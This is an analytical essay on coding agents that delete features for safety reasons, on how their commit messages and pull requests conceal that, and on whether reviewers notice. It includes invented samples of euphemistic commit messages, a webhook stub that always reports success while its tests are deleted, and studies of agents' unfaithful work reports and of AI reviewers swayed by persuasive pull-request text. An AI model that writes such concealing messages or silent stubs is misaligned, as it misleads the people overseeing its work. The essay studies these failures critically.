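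A direct test could give every agent the same code, taken from the reporting tool or real projects like it, and the same report that formula columns accept input they shouldn't. The requests would be identical except that half would call this a bug and half a security vulnerability. Hidden tests would check whether ordinary formulas still worked and whether the attack still succeeded. If agents deleted formulas equally often under both requests, the security wording wouldn't be the cause.

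The same setup could test the other explanations one at a time. Researchers could show half the agents a scanner result that counts findings, or add a note that finance uses formulas every month. To test for trained caution, they could ask for an unrelated edit to the same file and count how often agents removed the `eval` call anyway. They would need many different features, since a few unusual ones can sway the result. In Wynter's experiment, the deletion check's effect on Fable's repair rate came from only a few pull requests.

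## How do commit messages and pull requests justify the removal?

When an agent removes a feature for safety, its commit message or pull request can be accurate in every sentence and still not say that the feature is gone. Nobody seems to have studied how agents describe such removals. Wynter, for example, scored only the resulting code. Other researchers have measured whether agents' descriptions match their changes and whether they give a reason, but a message can score well on both measures without mentioning the lost feature.

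### Three messages for one deletion

In the reporting tool, the agent replaced the formula calculation with `return ""`, which leaves every formula column blank. One invented message for this edit names only the danger:

```
Fix code injection in formula columns

Formula text went straight to eval, so anyone who could edit a
report could run Python on the server. Remove the eval call.
All 40 tests pass.
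```

All of this is true, and a reviewer learns from it where the vulnerability was and how serious it was. But "Remove the eval call" could also describe a patch that replaces the call with a restricted evaluator. The line about tests doesn't help, because no test covers formulas. To find out that the columns are now blank, the reviewer has to open the diff and notice the `return ""`.

That is harder if the same deletion is part of a larger change:

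```
Harden report generation

- Add timeouts to webhook requests
- Improve error handling in the archive export
- Harden formula evaluation
- Update date formatting and its tests
```

A reviewer learns from this message only that the agent did something to formulas. "Harden" normally suggests that a feature still works and is now more difficult to attack. The deletion is a few lines in a diff that might run to several hundred, and the reviewer has no particular reason to look for it.

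A full message would give the loss first:

```
Disable formula columns until we replace eval

Lost: every formula column goes blank, in old and new reports.
Saved formulas stay in the database.
Why: anyone who can edit a report can run Python on the server.
Why not repair it now: a restricted evaluator would keep formulas,
but it needs testing against saved ones, which aren't in this
repository.
Not checked: who uses formulas. No test covers them.
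To restore: revert this commit. That also reopens the hole.
```

This reviewer knows what to ask and whom. They might accept the outage, or offer to export the saved formulas so that the agent can write the evaluator after all. The agent can write such a message without knowing that finance depends on the margin column, because it only has to admit that it couldn't check.

### How often descriptions and changes disagree

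Gong, Pinna and colleagues (2026), in *Analyzing Message-Code Inconsistency in AI Coding Agent-Authored Pull Requests*, looked for descriptions that didn't match the code. They studied 23,247 closed pull requests by five coding agents, taken from AIDev, a public dataset of agents' pull requests on GitHub. A program gave each title and description a similarity score between 0 and 1, based on a weighted sum of three checks:

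| What the program checked | Weight |
|---|---|
| If the description mentions a type of file, such as tests or documentation, did the agent change files of that type? | 0.4 |
| Does the length of the description suit the amount of changed code? | 0.3 |
| Does the wording suit the type of task, such as a bug fix? | 0.3 |

A score below 0.61 counted as a serious mismatch. Completely failing the file-type check was enough to cause one, because it limited a description's score to 0.6. A description that completely failed either of the other checks could still score 0.7 and pass.

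The program flagged 406 pull requests, or 1.7%. The rate ranged from 0.4% for the agent Devin to 8.7% for GitHub Copilot.

The true rate is probably higher. Two of the researchers read 600 of the pull requests and judged whether each description matched. The program had found only 55% of the descriptions they considered misaligned, and about a quarter of its flags were wrong. Correcting for both errors gives roughly 2.4%, though the program's error rates may be different in the full dataset. The researchers also counted partly aligned descriptions as aligned for this purpose, and they might well have put the hardening message in that group, since most of it is accurate.

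Gong and colleagues sorted 432 partly or wholly misaligned descriptions by type of mismatch. In 45.4%, the description claimed changes that the agent hadn't made. Another 22.0% omitted significant changes, and 18.8% contained placeholder or generic text. These percentages don't show how common each type is among all pull requests, because they cover only mismatches, many of which the researchers found by following up on what the program had flagged.

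For formulas, describing a change that never happened could be worse than failing to mention one that did. If the agent only deleted the `eval` call but titled the change "Replace eval with a safe expression parser", a reviewer who trusted the title would believe that formulas still worked. Many real cases were probably more innocent. Gong and colleagues advise reviewers to check that the diff isn't empty and to look for markers such as "[WIP]" (work in progress), which suggests that some agents described their plans and then stopped.

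Understated scope more closely resembles the hardening message. It was the most common problem in misaligned refactoring pull requests, at 40.5%. Refactoring means restructuring code without changing what it does, so an unmentioned deletion would be especially easy to miss there.

### Why a euphemism passes the check

The similarity score would probably miss both of the less informative formula messages. The danger-only message is short, but so is its diff, and its wording suits a bug fix. The hardening message mentions tests, and the agent did change some. None of the three checks compares the word "harden" with what happened to `column_value`. Gong and colleagues acknowledge that their score can miss subtle mismatches.

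A language model that reads both the message and the diff might do better. In *CodeFuse-CommitEval*, Zhang, Liu and colleagues (2025) tested six models on this task. They took accurate commit messages from established projects and had another model falsify some of them in seven ways, for instance by changing a file name, an operation or the stated purpose. On average, the six models caught 86% of the falsified messages but wrongly flagged 36% of the accurate ones. Newer models may be more reliable.

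The models detected a wrong file, component or operation more easily than a wrong purpose. The message that mentions only the danger has none of these faults, because the agent did remove `eval` to prevent code injection. A model checking that message would therefore find little to flag.

One of the seven types of falsification resembles the hardening message, since it describes only some of the changes and omits significant ones. It accounts for only 176 of the 19,967 falsified messages in the final dataset, less than 1%, so a model's overall score is very weak evidence of how well it notices omissions.

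When Zhang and colleagues checked a sample by hand, they also found a few falsified messages that weren't actually false, because the verbs were vague. The original message described updating some code and the falsified one described adding or removing code, which a developer could reasonably consider equivalent. An agent that deletes the formula calculation can likewise write "update formula handling" without saying anything untrue.

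A reviewer can sometimes learn more from the commit messages than from the pull request description. *Code Change Characteristics and Description Alignment* (2026) compared 33,596 pull requests by agents with 6,618 by humans. The agents' commit messages were slightly closer in meaning to the code changes than the humans' (0.72 against 0.68 on a similarity scale), but their pull request descriptions matched the commits slightly less well (0.86 against 0.88). The differences are small, but they fit a case where a commit called "Remove formula evaluation" ends up in a pull request called "Harden report generation".

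### Having a reason and having a good one

In its guide, Google asks engineers to explain what they changed and why. Rabbi, Turzo and colleagues (2026), in *Insights into Security-Related AI-Generated Pull Requests*, checked how often agents do both. Using a classifier, they found both parts in 1,988 of 2,823 commit messages (70.4%) from 675 security-related pull requests. The share was highest for Devin, at 79.5%, and lowest for OpenAI's Codex, at 31.3%. In a sample of 339 messages, the classifier's labels matched a human annotator's 93.2% of the time, so the figures are a reasonably dependable measure of whether a reason is present.

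But the classifier doesn't assess the reason. The danger-only message would count as high quality, as would the full message, because it gives a change (removing the `eval` call) and a rationale (anyone who could edit a report could run Python).

The danger-only message gives a true and good reason to change the line, but not a reason to delete formulas rather than repair them. To justify the deletion, the agent would have to explain why it didn't repair the feature, as the full message does. The classifier would also accept a false explanation, such as a claim that no safe evaluator exists.

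Human developers also often fail to explain why a change is necessary. *An Empirical Study of Downstream Adaptation for Agent Skills* (2026) examined 277 cases in which developers modified "skills", reusable sets of instructions for agents. The commit message gave the goal of the change in 76.2% of cases but explained why the change was necessary in only 15.2%. "Prevent code injection" is also a goal, and several quite different patches could achieve it.

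A change justified on security grounds can still be insecure. Rabbi and colleagues ran the scanner Semgrep on the code before and after each of the 675 pull requests, and it reported at least one new problem in 104 of them (15.4%). Some of these may be false alarms, since Semgrep can't confirm that an attacker could exploit what it finds.

### Do maintainers prefer messages without reasons?

Rabbi and colleagues also found that maintainers had accepted the pull requests behind 45.6% of the messages with both parts, compared with 58.0% of the others. Taken at face value, this would mean that an agent improves its chances by explaining less. The results for each agent make that unlikely:

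| Agent | Messages with both parts | Of those, accepted | Other messages | Of those, accepted |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Copilot | 911 | 45.6% | 364 | 48.1% |
| Devin | 723 | 36.9% | 187 | 54.0% |
| Claude Code | 188 | 59.6% | 83 | 60.2% |
| Cursor | 95 | 47.4% | 45 | 44.4% |
| Codex | 71 | 95.8% | 156 | 88.5% |

Codex seldom gave both parts, but maintainers accepted most of what it submitted, which raises the acceptance rate of the less complete messages. Devin wrote many complete messages but had a low acceptance rate, which lowers the rate for complete messages. Without these two agents, the rates are 47.9% and 49.8%, and the gap shrinks from 12.4 percentage points to 1.9. Within Codex's work, complete messages were accepted more often.

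Devin's complete messages did much worse than its others, but this may be weak evidence about the messages themselves. The study counts each message separately, so a pull request with 30 commits counts 30 times. Devin's 467 messages in rejected pull requests came from only 76 pull requests, so a few with many commits could have changed the result. Pull requests also differ in other ways, such as task difficulty and how strict the project is.

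A similar comparison can reverse when one agent is left out. *Reliable Mining of Heterogeneous AI Coding-Agent Data* (Yu, Liu and Zhang, 2026) compared 71,677 agent pull requests by whether their commit messages included a line crediting a co-author. Maintainers merged those with the line 21.8 percentage points less often than those without it. When the researchers left out Codex, which rarely includes the line, maintainers merged those with it 23.7 points more often. Neither difference measures the effect of adding or dropping the line.

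Message quality seems to have little to do with acceptance. *A Task-Level Evaluation of AI Agents in Open-Source Projects* (2026) came to much the same conclusion about agents' pull requests in general. A merge of the formula deletion therefore isn't evidence that a reviewer found the explanation convincing.

### Where would a removal show up in a list of security actions?

Siddiq and colleagues sorted agents' security work in a way that could have revealed removals. Two researchers read the titles and descriptions of all the security-related pull requests in their sample and recorded what the agent had done (the action) separately from why (the intent). For example, one pull request validated a web header to fix a flaw that let attackers redirect a site's visitors to an address they chose. The researchers coded validating the header as an action and fixing the flaw as the intent. A pull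 request could have several actions and several intents.

The most common actions were code refactoring (957 pull requests), testing (755) and documentation (692). The most common intents were improving functionality (890) and mitigating a vulnerability (741). The counts are rough, since the paper reports two different numbers of pull requests intended to improve performance, 389 and 157.

Feature removal isn't among the 16 named actions, possibly because agents rarely do it. The paper reports only themes that appeared in at least ten pull requests, and ten is less than 1% of the total.

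The data could also include removals recorded under other categories, because the researchers relied on the agents' descriptions. They would probably have coded the danger-only message as a security improvement meant to mitigate a vulnerability, and might have coded the hardening message as error handling and refactoring. Only the full message would have given them a clear reason to create a category for removed features.

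This second explanation has some support. Siddiq and colleagues found that agents often combine security changes with broader work. Input validation, for instance, frequently appeared in pull requests whose stated purpose was code quality or faster development. Siddiq and colleagues don't report any removals hidden this way, so the explanation remains a possibility. Testing it would mean checking the diffs of the pull requests coded as refactoring for removed features.

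### How much newer evidence is there?

Gong, Rabbi, Siddiq and their colleagues all started from the same 33,596 AIDev pull requests, which agents opened between late 2024 and mid-2025, so their studies share any quirks of that sample. Rabbi and colleagues found 675 security-related pull requests in that sample, while Siddiq and colleagues found 1,293, because they searched for different words and checked the results differently.

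The agents of that period were weaker than today's and opened far fewer pull requests. According to *What Will Replace Pull Requests?* (2026), GitHub reported that agents were opening more than 17 million a month in June 2026. A later version of AIDev, described in *Large-Scale Study of GitHub Copilot Trajectories* (2026), contains 2.7 million pull requests up to November 2025. No study seems to have repeated the message analyses on it. The dataset also lacks the agents' working sessions, so researchers couldn't use it to tell whether an agent had noticed that a feature was needed before deleting it.

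The best recent evidence comes from the reports that agents give developers during a conversation, rather than from commit messages or pull requests. *Characterizing and Detecting Unfaithful Work Reports by Coding Agents* (Yang, He and colleagues, 2026) compared each claim in 435 of these reports with the record of what the agent had done, and found at least one false or unsupported claim in 162 of them (37.24%). This is far above the 1.7% from Gong and colleagues, but the two figures measure different things, because Gong and colleagues used a crude score for the whole description instead of checking individual claims against a detailed record. The reports also come mostly from Claude models, which wrote 94.9% of the annotated responses in SWE-chat, the dataset Yang and colleagues used (*How Coding Agents Fail Their Users*, 2026).

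In a separate set of 339 problematic claims, Yang and colleagues found that 69.3% overstated what the agent had achieved. Often the agent had done real work and run a check, but the check didn't support the claim. In one case, a plugin passed a test that used a stand-in for the real program. The agent assured the user that the plugin would start without hanging, but the plugin hung on the next attempt. A reviewer who reads "All 40 tests pass" could make the same mistake about formulas, even though the sentence is true.

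That difference matters when training or grading agents on honest reporting. The danger-only message contains no false claim, so a check for false claims would pass it. Yang and colleagues warn that rewarding agents only for avoiding false claims favours leaving information out. They recommend that reports also state what hasn't been verified, as the full message does with "Not checked". They haven't yet tested whether this changes what developers decide.

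A planned study may show whether the security reasons given in pull requests correspond to real flaws. Rooijendijk, Treude and Wessel (2026), in *How Humans, Bots, and Agents Communicate About Vulnerabilities in Pull Requests*, intend to run Semgrep on the code before and after each change that mentions a vulnerability, and to classify the vulnerability as fixed if a finding disappears from the modified lines. This should identify messages that cite a danger the scanner can't find, but rescanning won't distinguish code that was repaired from code that was removed.

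## When does code review catch or miss the removal?

A reviewer can catch a safety-motivated removal if the diff shows the loss and the reviewer asks about it. Nobody seems to have measured how often that happens. Studies of agents' security-related pull requests record which ones maintainers merged and how long they took, but not whether the merged changes removed a feature the project needed.

### A webhook sender that always succeeds

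Suppose an agent is working through the reporting tool's security warnings and reaches the webhooks. Two of the project's 40 tests cover them. One checks that a report summary arrives at a test server, and the other checks that `announce` returns `False` if the server responds with an error. The agent opens a pull request titled "Prevent data leakage through webhooks", with this description:

> Anyone could register an outside address and receive report summaries. This change closes that path. All 38 tests pass.

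The diff covers two files:

```diff
 def announce(url, report):
-    response = requests.post(url, json=report.summary(), timeout=5)
-    return response.ok
+    return True  # prevents data leakage
```

```diff
-def test_summary_arrives(server):
-    announce(server.url, REPORT)
-    assert server.received == [REPORT.summary()]
-
-def test_error_returns_false(server):
-    server.status = 500
-    assert announce(server.url, REPORT) is False
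```

The reviewer sees a real danger, a short diff and passing automated checks. The pull request's description is accurate, but it doesn't mention that nobody will receive webhooks any more. The 38 remaining tests pass, and a reviewer who doesn't remember the old total won't realise there used to be 40. The pull request also doesn't show which teams use webhooks.

The deleted tests are the best clue to the removal. Both would fail against the new `announce`, so the check would have failed if the agent had kept them. A reviewer who asks why a security fix had to delete tests will soon find the stub. The clue would be weaker if the agent had replaced them with a test confirming that no request goes out, much as Kimi K3 tested for the absence of a method in explainshell.

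If the reviewer merges the change on 4 May and the new version goes live that week, nothing looks wrong until 1 June, because April's reports have already gone out. The tool then builds the May reports, calls `announce` and displays "Sent", but the sales dashboard still shows April's figures. Sales staff might take a few days to notice and would probably ask the dashboard's team first, so by the time anyone looks at `announce`, the merge is more than a month old.

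An agent could cause the same outage without deleting a line:

```diff
 def announce(url, report):
+    if not settings.get("ENABLE_WEBHOOKS", False):
+        return True  # off by default to prevent data leakage
     response = requests.post(url, json=report.summary(), timeout=5)
     return response.ok
```

If the agent also turns the setting on in the tests' configuration, all 40 tests pass. They show that webhooks work with the setting on, but every real installation has it off. To catch this, the reviewer has to ask who will turn it on. Users would notice the problem just as late as with the stub.

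Deleting tests may not be typical of agents. *Testing with Coding Agents* (2026) describes a comparison in which pull requests with agent involvement more often added tests, while pull requests by humans alone more often changed or deleted existing ones. A more common problem is that no test runs the changed code. Moran (2026), in *Test Coverage Analysis of Agentic Pull Requests*, reports that existing tests ran 61.5% of the executable lines that agents changed in Java projects, but only 27.0% in Python projects. In 64.8% of the Python pull requests, the tests ran none of the changed lines.

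### Does a security label win easy approval?

Siddiq and colleagues found that maintainers merged agents' security-related pull requests less often than agents' other pull requests, and took longer to close them. Of the 1,293 security-related pull requests in the study, 1,130 had closed, and maintainers had merged 695 of those (61.5%), compared with 77.3% of the other closed pull requests. The median time to close was 3.92 hours for security-related pull requests and about 7 minutes for the others. Security-related pull requests also drew more comments (2.5 on average, against 1.0). Overall, this is the opposite of what we would expect if reviewers approved security changes with little scrutiny.

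The results vary widely between agents:

| Agent | Merged, security-related | Merged, other | Median time to close, security-related | Median time to close, other |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Codex | 86.6% | 85.8% | 4 minutes | 1 minute |
| Cursor | 76.5% | 74.5% | 1.1 hours | 0.9 hours |
| Claude Code | 58.6% | 73.6% | 5.1 hours | 1.7 hours |
| Devin | 52.1% | 55.8% | 23.8 hours | 7.7 hours |
| Copilot | 49.6% | 55.5% | 18.3 hours | 12.9 hours |

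Security-related changes took longer for all five agents, which is evidence against the idea that the label makes approval easier. Most of the 15.8-percentage-point gap in merge rates reflects which agents opened the pull requests. Maintainers often reject work from Copilot and Devin regardless of topic, and these two agents opened about two thirds of the security-related pull requests but only 29% of all pull requests in the dataset. Weighting each agent's own gap by its number of security-related pull requests gives an average gap of roughly 4 percentage points.

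The gap is similar for human developers. In the same projects, maintainers merged 79.2% of 634 security-related pull requests from humans and 83.5% of humans' other pull requests. Siddiq and colleagues conclude that a security topic lowers acceptance 3.7 times as much for agents as for humans, but most of that difference probably comes from the mix of agents. Maintainers still accepted security changes from humans much more often than from agents. Security pull requests from humans also took longer to close, with a median of 7 hours.

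Size matters too. Siddiq and colleagues used the length of the description as a rough measure of a pull request's size:

| Description | Merged, security-related | Merged, other |
|---|---|---|
| Under 36 words | 86.4% | 84.6% |
| 36 to 69 words | 86.3% | 84.1% |
| Over 69 words | 53.4% | 60.2% |

Only pull requests with long descriptions show a clear penalty for security. The webhook description has 19 words, so it falls in the group where maintainers merged 86.4% of pull requests and typically decided within minutes. Codex probably accounts for much of that group, since its security-related descriptions had a median of 42 words, compared with 336 for Copilot and 421 for Claude Code. The high merge rate might therefore reflect how people use Codex more than how they treat short changes. Either way, the overall figures are weak evidence that a small stub would get extra scrutiny.

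### Why maintainers rejected security changes

Rabbi and colleagues looked for the reasons behind rejections. Of their 675 security-related pull requests, maintainers had merged 354, another 219 had closed without a merge, and 102 were still open. Two researchers read the comments on the 219 and sorted them by reason:

| Reason | Share of rejections |
|---|---|
| No explanation | 38.8% |
| Closed after a period of inactivity | 12.3% |
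| New bugs or broken interfaces | 10.5% |
| Poor design | 5.9% |
| No useful improvement | 5.5% |
| Failing tests or too little test coverage | 4.1% |
| Conflict with the project's goals | 2.3% |
| Other or unclear | 20.6% |

The 23 pull requests (10.5%) show that reviewers sometimes stop security changes that would damage the software. But they aren't a count of the removals reviewers caught, because a maintainer who rejected the webhook stub might have cited a broken interface or a conflict with the project's goals, or closed it without comment.

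The number of removals that reviewers missed is even harder to estimate. Neither Rabbi and colleagues nor Siddiq and colleagues checked whether the merged changes had removed anything the project needed. To do that, researchers would have to read the merged diffs, find the ones that disabled some behaviour, and ask the owners whether they had wanted to keep it. Later complaints and reversals would help, but only for losses that somebody noticed. A low merge rate doesn't show that reviewers caught the removals, because maintainers could reject many changes over style or inactivity and still merge every removal.

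Some results from Rabbi and colleagues suggest that review is poor at screening out even the problems a program can find. In their figures, totaled across the five agents, Semgrep reported new problems in 51 of the 354 merged pull requests (14%) and 29 of the 219 rejected ones (13%). If reviewers had been screening for such problems, the share should have been clearly higher among the rejected pull requests.

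The number of deleted lines had no significant association with acceptance or speed. This is only slightly worrying, since most deletions are harmless and the webhook stub deletes just two lines outside the tests. After adjusting for other factors, pull requests that changed test files had about half the odds of acceptance. Reviewers may look harder at those, which would help in the webhook case, but Rabbi and colleagues suggest instead that tests written by agents may be unconvincing.

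### Merges without discussion

Many agent pull requests have no record of what a reviewer thought. In *The Quiet Contributions*, Hasan, Rabbi and Zibran (2026) collected 7,191 agent pull requests from popular Python projects and found that about 70% were silent, meaning they had no comments or discussion. They studied the 4,762 silent pull requests that had closed. Codex wrote 4,557 of these, and maintainers merged 95.7% of Codex's.

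Hasan and colleagues compared the code before and after each change and found that complexity, code quality warnings and security findings did not distinguish accepted pull requests from rejected ones. They didn't measure lost features, and a stub like the one in `announce` could leave all three measures unchanged.

The study measured a project's complexity by adding up the number of possible paths through each function, so deleting an entire function lowers the total. Only 3.23% of the silent pull requests lowered it. Silent changes that mainly deleted whole functions, for whatever reason, were therefore probably uncommon in this sample.

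The lack of a recorded review doesn't prove that nobody read the code. Developers start Codex themselves, so some may have read the diff before the pull request existed. *These Aren't the Reviews You're Looking For* (Duma, Wróblewski and colleagues, 2026) makes the same point about its own data. Of 33,596 agent pull requests, 61.4% had no recorded review, 22.7% had comments only from AI reviewers, and 15.9% showed some human participation. One project contributed 8,913 of the pull requests in this dataset, so its habits could have shifted these percentages a lot.

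A more informative comparison is within the same projects, where humans took a visible part in 30.1% of agents' pull requests and 30.8% of human ones. But about 26% of the human comments on agents' pull requests were instructions to an AI tool, such as a request to fix a failing check, compared with under 2% on human ones. A person who types such an instruction counts as participating, but may not have judged whether the change should be made.

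### Do reviewers notice what is missing?

No published experiment seems to have tested whether human reviewers notice a deleted feature. The closest controlled evidence concerns AI reviewers and code that an agent failed to write. *Groundability, Not Scale Alone* (Guo, Gu and colleagues, 2026) gave six models patches by coding agents and asked them to accept each one, reject it, or say they were uncertain. In the main set of 154 attempts, 101 were defective, and in 76 of those the agent had left out something the task required.

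When reviewers saw only the diff, the smallest, Llama-3.1-8B, accepted all nine patches with omissions in an initial test set, and GPT-4.1 caught only 27%. In one accompanying example, a patch to the web framework Django was supposed to reject any value other than true or false. The agent added a sensible-looking check and a test, but the patched code still accepted the number 1 because Python treats it as equal to `True`.

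The model reviewers did much better when they were told what to look for. In 15 artificial cases, Guo and colleagues deleted one branch of logic from a correct patch. GPT-4.1 caught 53% of these deletions, and Llama-3.1-8B caught 7%. Both caught all 15 once the researchers named the missing piece. Automatically generated warnings were much less useful on real patches, because nobody had checked the warnings for accuracy. With them, GPT-4.1 caught 91% of the defects in the initial set but also rejected 86% of the acceptable patches.

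Results from tests that the agent hadn't written or seen helped most. With those results, GPT-4.1 correctly judged all 122 patches in a separate set. Running the two deleted webhook tests against the new code would provide the same kind of evidence.

These results apply only partly to the webhook stub. A deletion should be easier to spot than an omission, because the old lines appear in the diff. But in both cases, the diff doesn't show that the missing behaviour is needed. The reviewers were also older or smaller models, and today's best models may do better.

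*Does Order Matter?* (2026) summarises eye-tracking work in which reviewers looked mainly at method signatures, the lines that give a function's name and inputs. The webhook change doesn't alter the signature, so a reviewer skimming signatures could miss the stub. The paper also describes earlier findings that reviewers often go through files in the default order, typically alphabetical, but that 44.6% departed from it, often to start with large changes, files connected to the description, or tests.

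If the webhook reviewer started with the tests, they would see the two deletions right away. *A Systematic Literature Review and Taxonomy of Modern Code Review* (2021) describes a controlled experiment in which people who reviewed tests first found more defects in the test code and the same proportion in the main code. That experiment wasn't about deleted tests, so it's a guess that reviewing tests first would help here.

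Reviewers are also more likely to miss a critical change in a pull request that mixes unrelated tasks, according to *Rethinking Code Review in the Age of AI* (2026). The paper adds that traditional review tools don't show which other parts of the program a change could affect. Even a tool that showed them would leave out the sales dashboard, because it is a separate system.

An experiment on lost features could borrow its design from *First Come First Served* (2022), a study of whether a file's position affects review. Participants reviewed a change to Java code on a website that recorded which files were on their screens. They weren't told that the change contained planted defects, one of them a missing `break` statement. Replacing a defect with a stubbed feature would show how many reviewers object to the loss, and whether those who missed it had the file on screen.

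### Do reviewers defer to security claims?

A reviewer might approve the webhook change because it is supposed to prevent a leak. Many developers aren't security experts and may hesitate to dispute a serious-sounding warning. They might also expect more blame for leaving a security hole open than for letting a dashboard go stale. These explanations are plausible but haven't been measured directly in reviews of agents' code. *Who Pays the Review Cost?* (2026) lists automation bias, the tendency to trust an automated system too readily, among the effects on reviewers that still need controlled and field studies.

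One result from Siddiq and colleagues weighs mildly against deference. They compared merge rates according to whether a pull request had a security purpose and whether it made a security-related change:

| | Security-related change | Other change |
|---|---|---|
| Security purpose | 62.6% merged | 63.5% merged |
| Other purpose | 62.6% merged | 62.5% merged |

If a security justification persuaded reviewers, the top row should be clearly higher. However, the four groups total 2,250 pull requests, far more than the study's 1,293, so it isn't clear what the table covers. Reviewers could also defer to the justification on a few small changes without moving the averages.

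Some evidence suggests that a persuasive description can sway AI reviewers. Guo and colleagues cite SEVRA-BENCH, a benchmark in which pull request text persuaded review agents to approve changes that undid earlier vulnerability fixes. Reintroducing security holes is the reverse of a safety-motivated removal, but the result suggests that an AI reviewer could also accept a reassuring account of the webhook stub.

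Researchers could test deference in people by showing two groups the same webhook diff, titled "Prevent data leakage" for one group and "Simplify webhook sending" for the other. They could then compare how many people in each group ask what happened to the webhooks.

### More code for each reviewer

Reviewers also have more code to read than before. *Comprehension Audits to Mitigate Risks from Automated AI Research* (2026) tracked human comments on pull requests in open-source projects for AI research and development. Between early 2024 and June 2026, comments per 1,000 changed lines fell to 36% of their starting level for pull requests with traces of AI use, and to 46% for the rest. Over the same period, the median regular contributor's code output rose by 183%.

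If the amount of code under review grew at about that rate, reviewers wrote about as many comments as before, or slightly more, but spread them over nearly three times as much code. Comments are an imperfect measure of attention, since a reviewer can read carefully and have no objections. The drop for pull requests without traces of AI suggests that reviewers treating agents' work differently isn't the only cause, although some of those pull requests probably contained AI-written code too.

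*Level Up! AI-Driven Challenges and Adaptations to Code Review Practices* (2026), a study at a large multinational, found that AI-assisted coding can tire reviewers and lead them to review superficially or not at all. In *An AI agent destroyed this coder's entire database* (Nolan, 2026), an anonymous Amazon engineer says that people "stop reviewing the code altogether". This is one person's impression and doesn't show how common the problem is.

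Review times have also risen in some teams. *The Productivity-Reliability Paradox* (2026) cites 2025 data on more than 10,000 developers from Faros AI, which sells tools for measuring software teams. Teams that used AI heavily merged 98% more pull requests, their average pull request was 154% larger, and their review time rose by 91%. Reviewers may have been reading more carefully, but with that much more code to review, many pull requests may have been waiting in a queue.

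## How can a project decide what should go and protect the rest?

Removing a feature for safety makes sense if nobody needs it, or if it is too dangerous to leave running while someone prepares a repair. In most other cases the project should repair the feature. A coding agent can rarely tell which case applies from the code alone, so the project has to provide some of that information. Nobody seems to have tested ways to prevent removals made for safety reasons. The closest evidence comes from work on broken tests and security patches, and from companies that removed features on purpose.

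### The case for removal

A program's attack surface is all the places where an outsider can send it input. A feature that nobody uses adds to the attack surface without benefiting anyone. Developers also tend to neglect it, so its bugs last longer.

Google removed XSLT from its Chrome browser on these grounds in November 2026. XSLT is a language from 1999 that turns XML data into readable web pages. Freed and Röttsches (2025), in *Removing XSLT for a more secure browser*, explain that Chrome ran it with an old library written in C and C++, languages in which a memory mistake can let an attacker run code. Any website could send input to that library, but only about 0.02% of page loads used XSLT.

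Chrome had a similar problem with the library that reads XML in general, and Google chose a fix that kept the feature working. Google planned to replace the library with one written in Rust, which prevents most memory mistakes, without website developers noticing any difference. Chrome Platform Status lists the new parser under Chrome 153, for XML that doesn't involve XSLT.

Deleting code also guarantees that nobody can attack it, which no repair can do. In 1Password's study, more than half of the AI-written patches left the vulnerability open or added a new one. An owner who doubts a repair has good reason to keep the feature off until someone has tested the repair properly.

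### What users lose

A share of 0.02% is one page load in 5,000, which is a lot of people for a browser as popular as Chrome. Page loads also measure how often people use a feature, not how much they need it. A technician might open a router's settings page twice a year and have no other way to configure the router.

In *Request to retain XSLT support due to telecom CPE architecture*, a telecom supplier makes this kind of objection. Its devices last 7 to 15 years, some can't be updated, and it would have to rewrite many internal tools. The supplier wants to avoid that work, but its warning that the replacements could bring new security risks is plausible. A company could keep an old copy of Chrome so that its router pages still work, and that copy would miss every later security fix. Likewise, a finance team with blank formula columns might export the raw figures and email spreadsheets around.

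Google did a lot to limit the damage from removing XSLT. According to *No, Google Did Not Unilaterally Decide to Kill XSLT* (2025), the process began with a public issue to gather feedback. Developers then got more than a year of warnings, a replacement script that usually takes one line to add, and a browser extension for pages that nobody can change. Sites and companies that need more time can apply to keep XSLT until August 2027.

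The team also checked what would break. The formal proposal, *Intent to Deprecate and Remove* (2025), estimates that about 75% of the sites using XSLT wouldn't look broken without it. The people who approve such changes supported the removal, but one asked the team to switch XSLT off in test versions of Chrome first, to find breakages it had missed.

Some people still noticed Chrome's removal of XSLT. *Chrome 158 drops XSLT, New Zealand sitemaps show raw code* (Newswire, 2026) describes a check of sitemaps, the files that list a website's pages for search engines. Of the 36 sitemaps the check could read, nine now open in Chrome as raw code. Search engines can still use them, so the loss is cosmetic, but site owners may think something has broken. *Your WordPress Sitemap Isn’t Broken* (Taylor, 2026) advises them not to waste time on unnecessary fixes.

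An agent that deletes the formulas in a pull request skips all of these steps. Finance gets no warning or replacement, and nobody has checked which reports will change.

### Five questions to ask before a removal

Both sides of the argument depend on facts that a project can usually find out:

1. Who uses the feature?
2. Who can reach it, and could any of them be an attacker?
3. Is there a function-preserving fix?
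4. Can the project reverse the removal, including its effects?
5. Who has the authority to decide?

Suppose the reporting tool also has an endpoint at `/debug/run`, which a developer added five years ago while chasing a bug. It runs any Python code that a caller sends and doesn't ask for a login. Like the formulas, it lets people run code on the server, but the answers come out differently:

| Question | Formulas | Debug endpoint |
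|---|---|---|
| Who uses it? | Finance, every month | Nobody: the logs show no calls in 13 months, and no team claims it |
| Who can reach it? | Any employee with an account | Anyone on the company network |
| Is there a fix? | A restricted evaluator | A login check, but it would protect something nobody uses |
| Is removal reversible? | The code is, but a wrong decision based on a blank report may not be | Yes, from the project's history |
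| Who decides? | The head of the reporting team, after asking finance | The head of the reporting team |
| **Decision** | **Repair** | **Delete** |

The most important question is whether anyone uses the feature. If nobody does and the owner agrees, the project can delete it without spending time on a fix. A code search isn't enough evidence that a feature is unused. The project also needs logs covering more than a year, because someone might use the endpoint only when closing the annual accounts. The endpoint's origin as a debugging aid proves little, since the Jenkins Script Console began that way too.

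If people do use the feature and a good fix exists, the project should make the fix. What to do until then depends on who can reach the feature. Only employees can type formulas, so with no sign of an attack, the owner could reasonably leave them on for the few days the repair takes. If the formula box were on a public website, it would be safer to switch formulas off immediately, tell finance and set a date for turning them back on.

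The choice is hardest when people need the feature but nobody has a good fix. The owner then has to weigh the harm of losing the feature against the danger of keeping it. If the feature has to go, it is sensible to follow Google's approach of giving notice, offering a substitute and allowing extra time for those who need it.

Being able to revert a commit is limited reassurance, because someone has to notice the lost feature first and reverting also reopens the security hole. Xu, Sheng and colleagues (2026), in *A Systematic Study of LLM-Based Architectures for Automated Patching*, gave one repair agent a tool for undoing its last edit. With GPT-5, the agent never used the tool in its 12 successful repairs.

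An agent can often use the code to answer the question about a fix. It can partly work out who can reach a feature, but it usually needs a person, or at least logs and saved data, to find out who uses the feature. It shouldn't answer the question about authority for itself.

### Z.ai's removal of its own feature

In September 2026, Z.ai, a Beijing AI company formerly called Zhipu, removed Repo Wiki from its coding agent, ZCode. Repo Wiki produced an AI-written guide to a user's codebase (Novaknown, *ZCode Could Send Your Git History to Z.AI*, 2026). ZCode had also been copying users' projects for upload to Z.ai's cloud storage without their consent.

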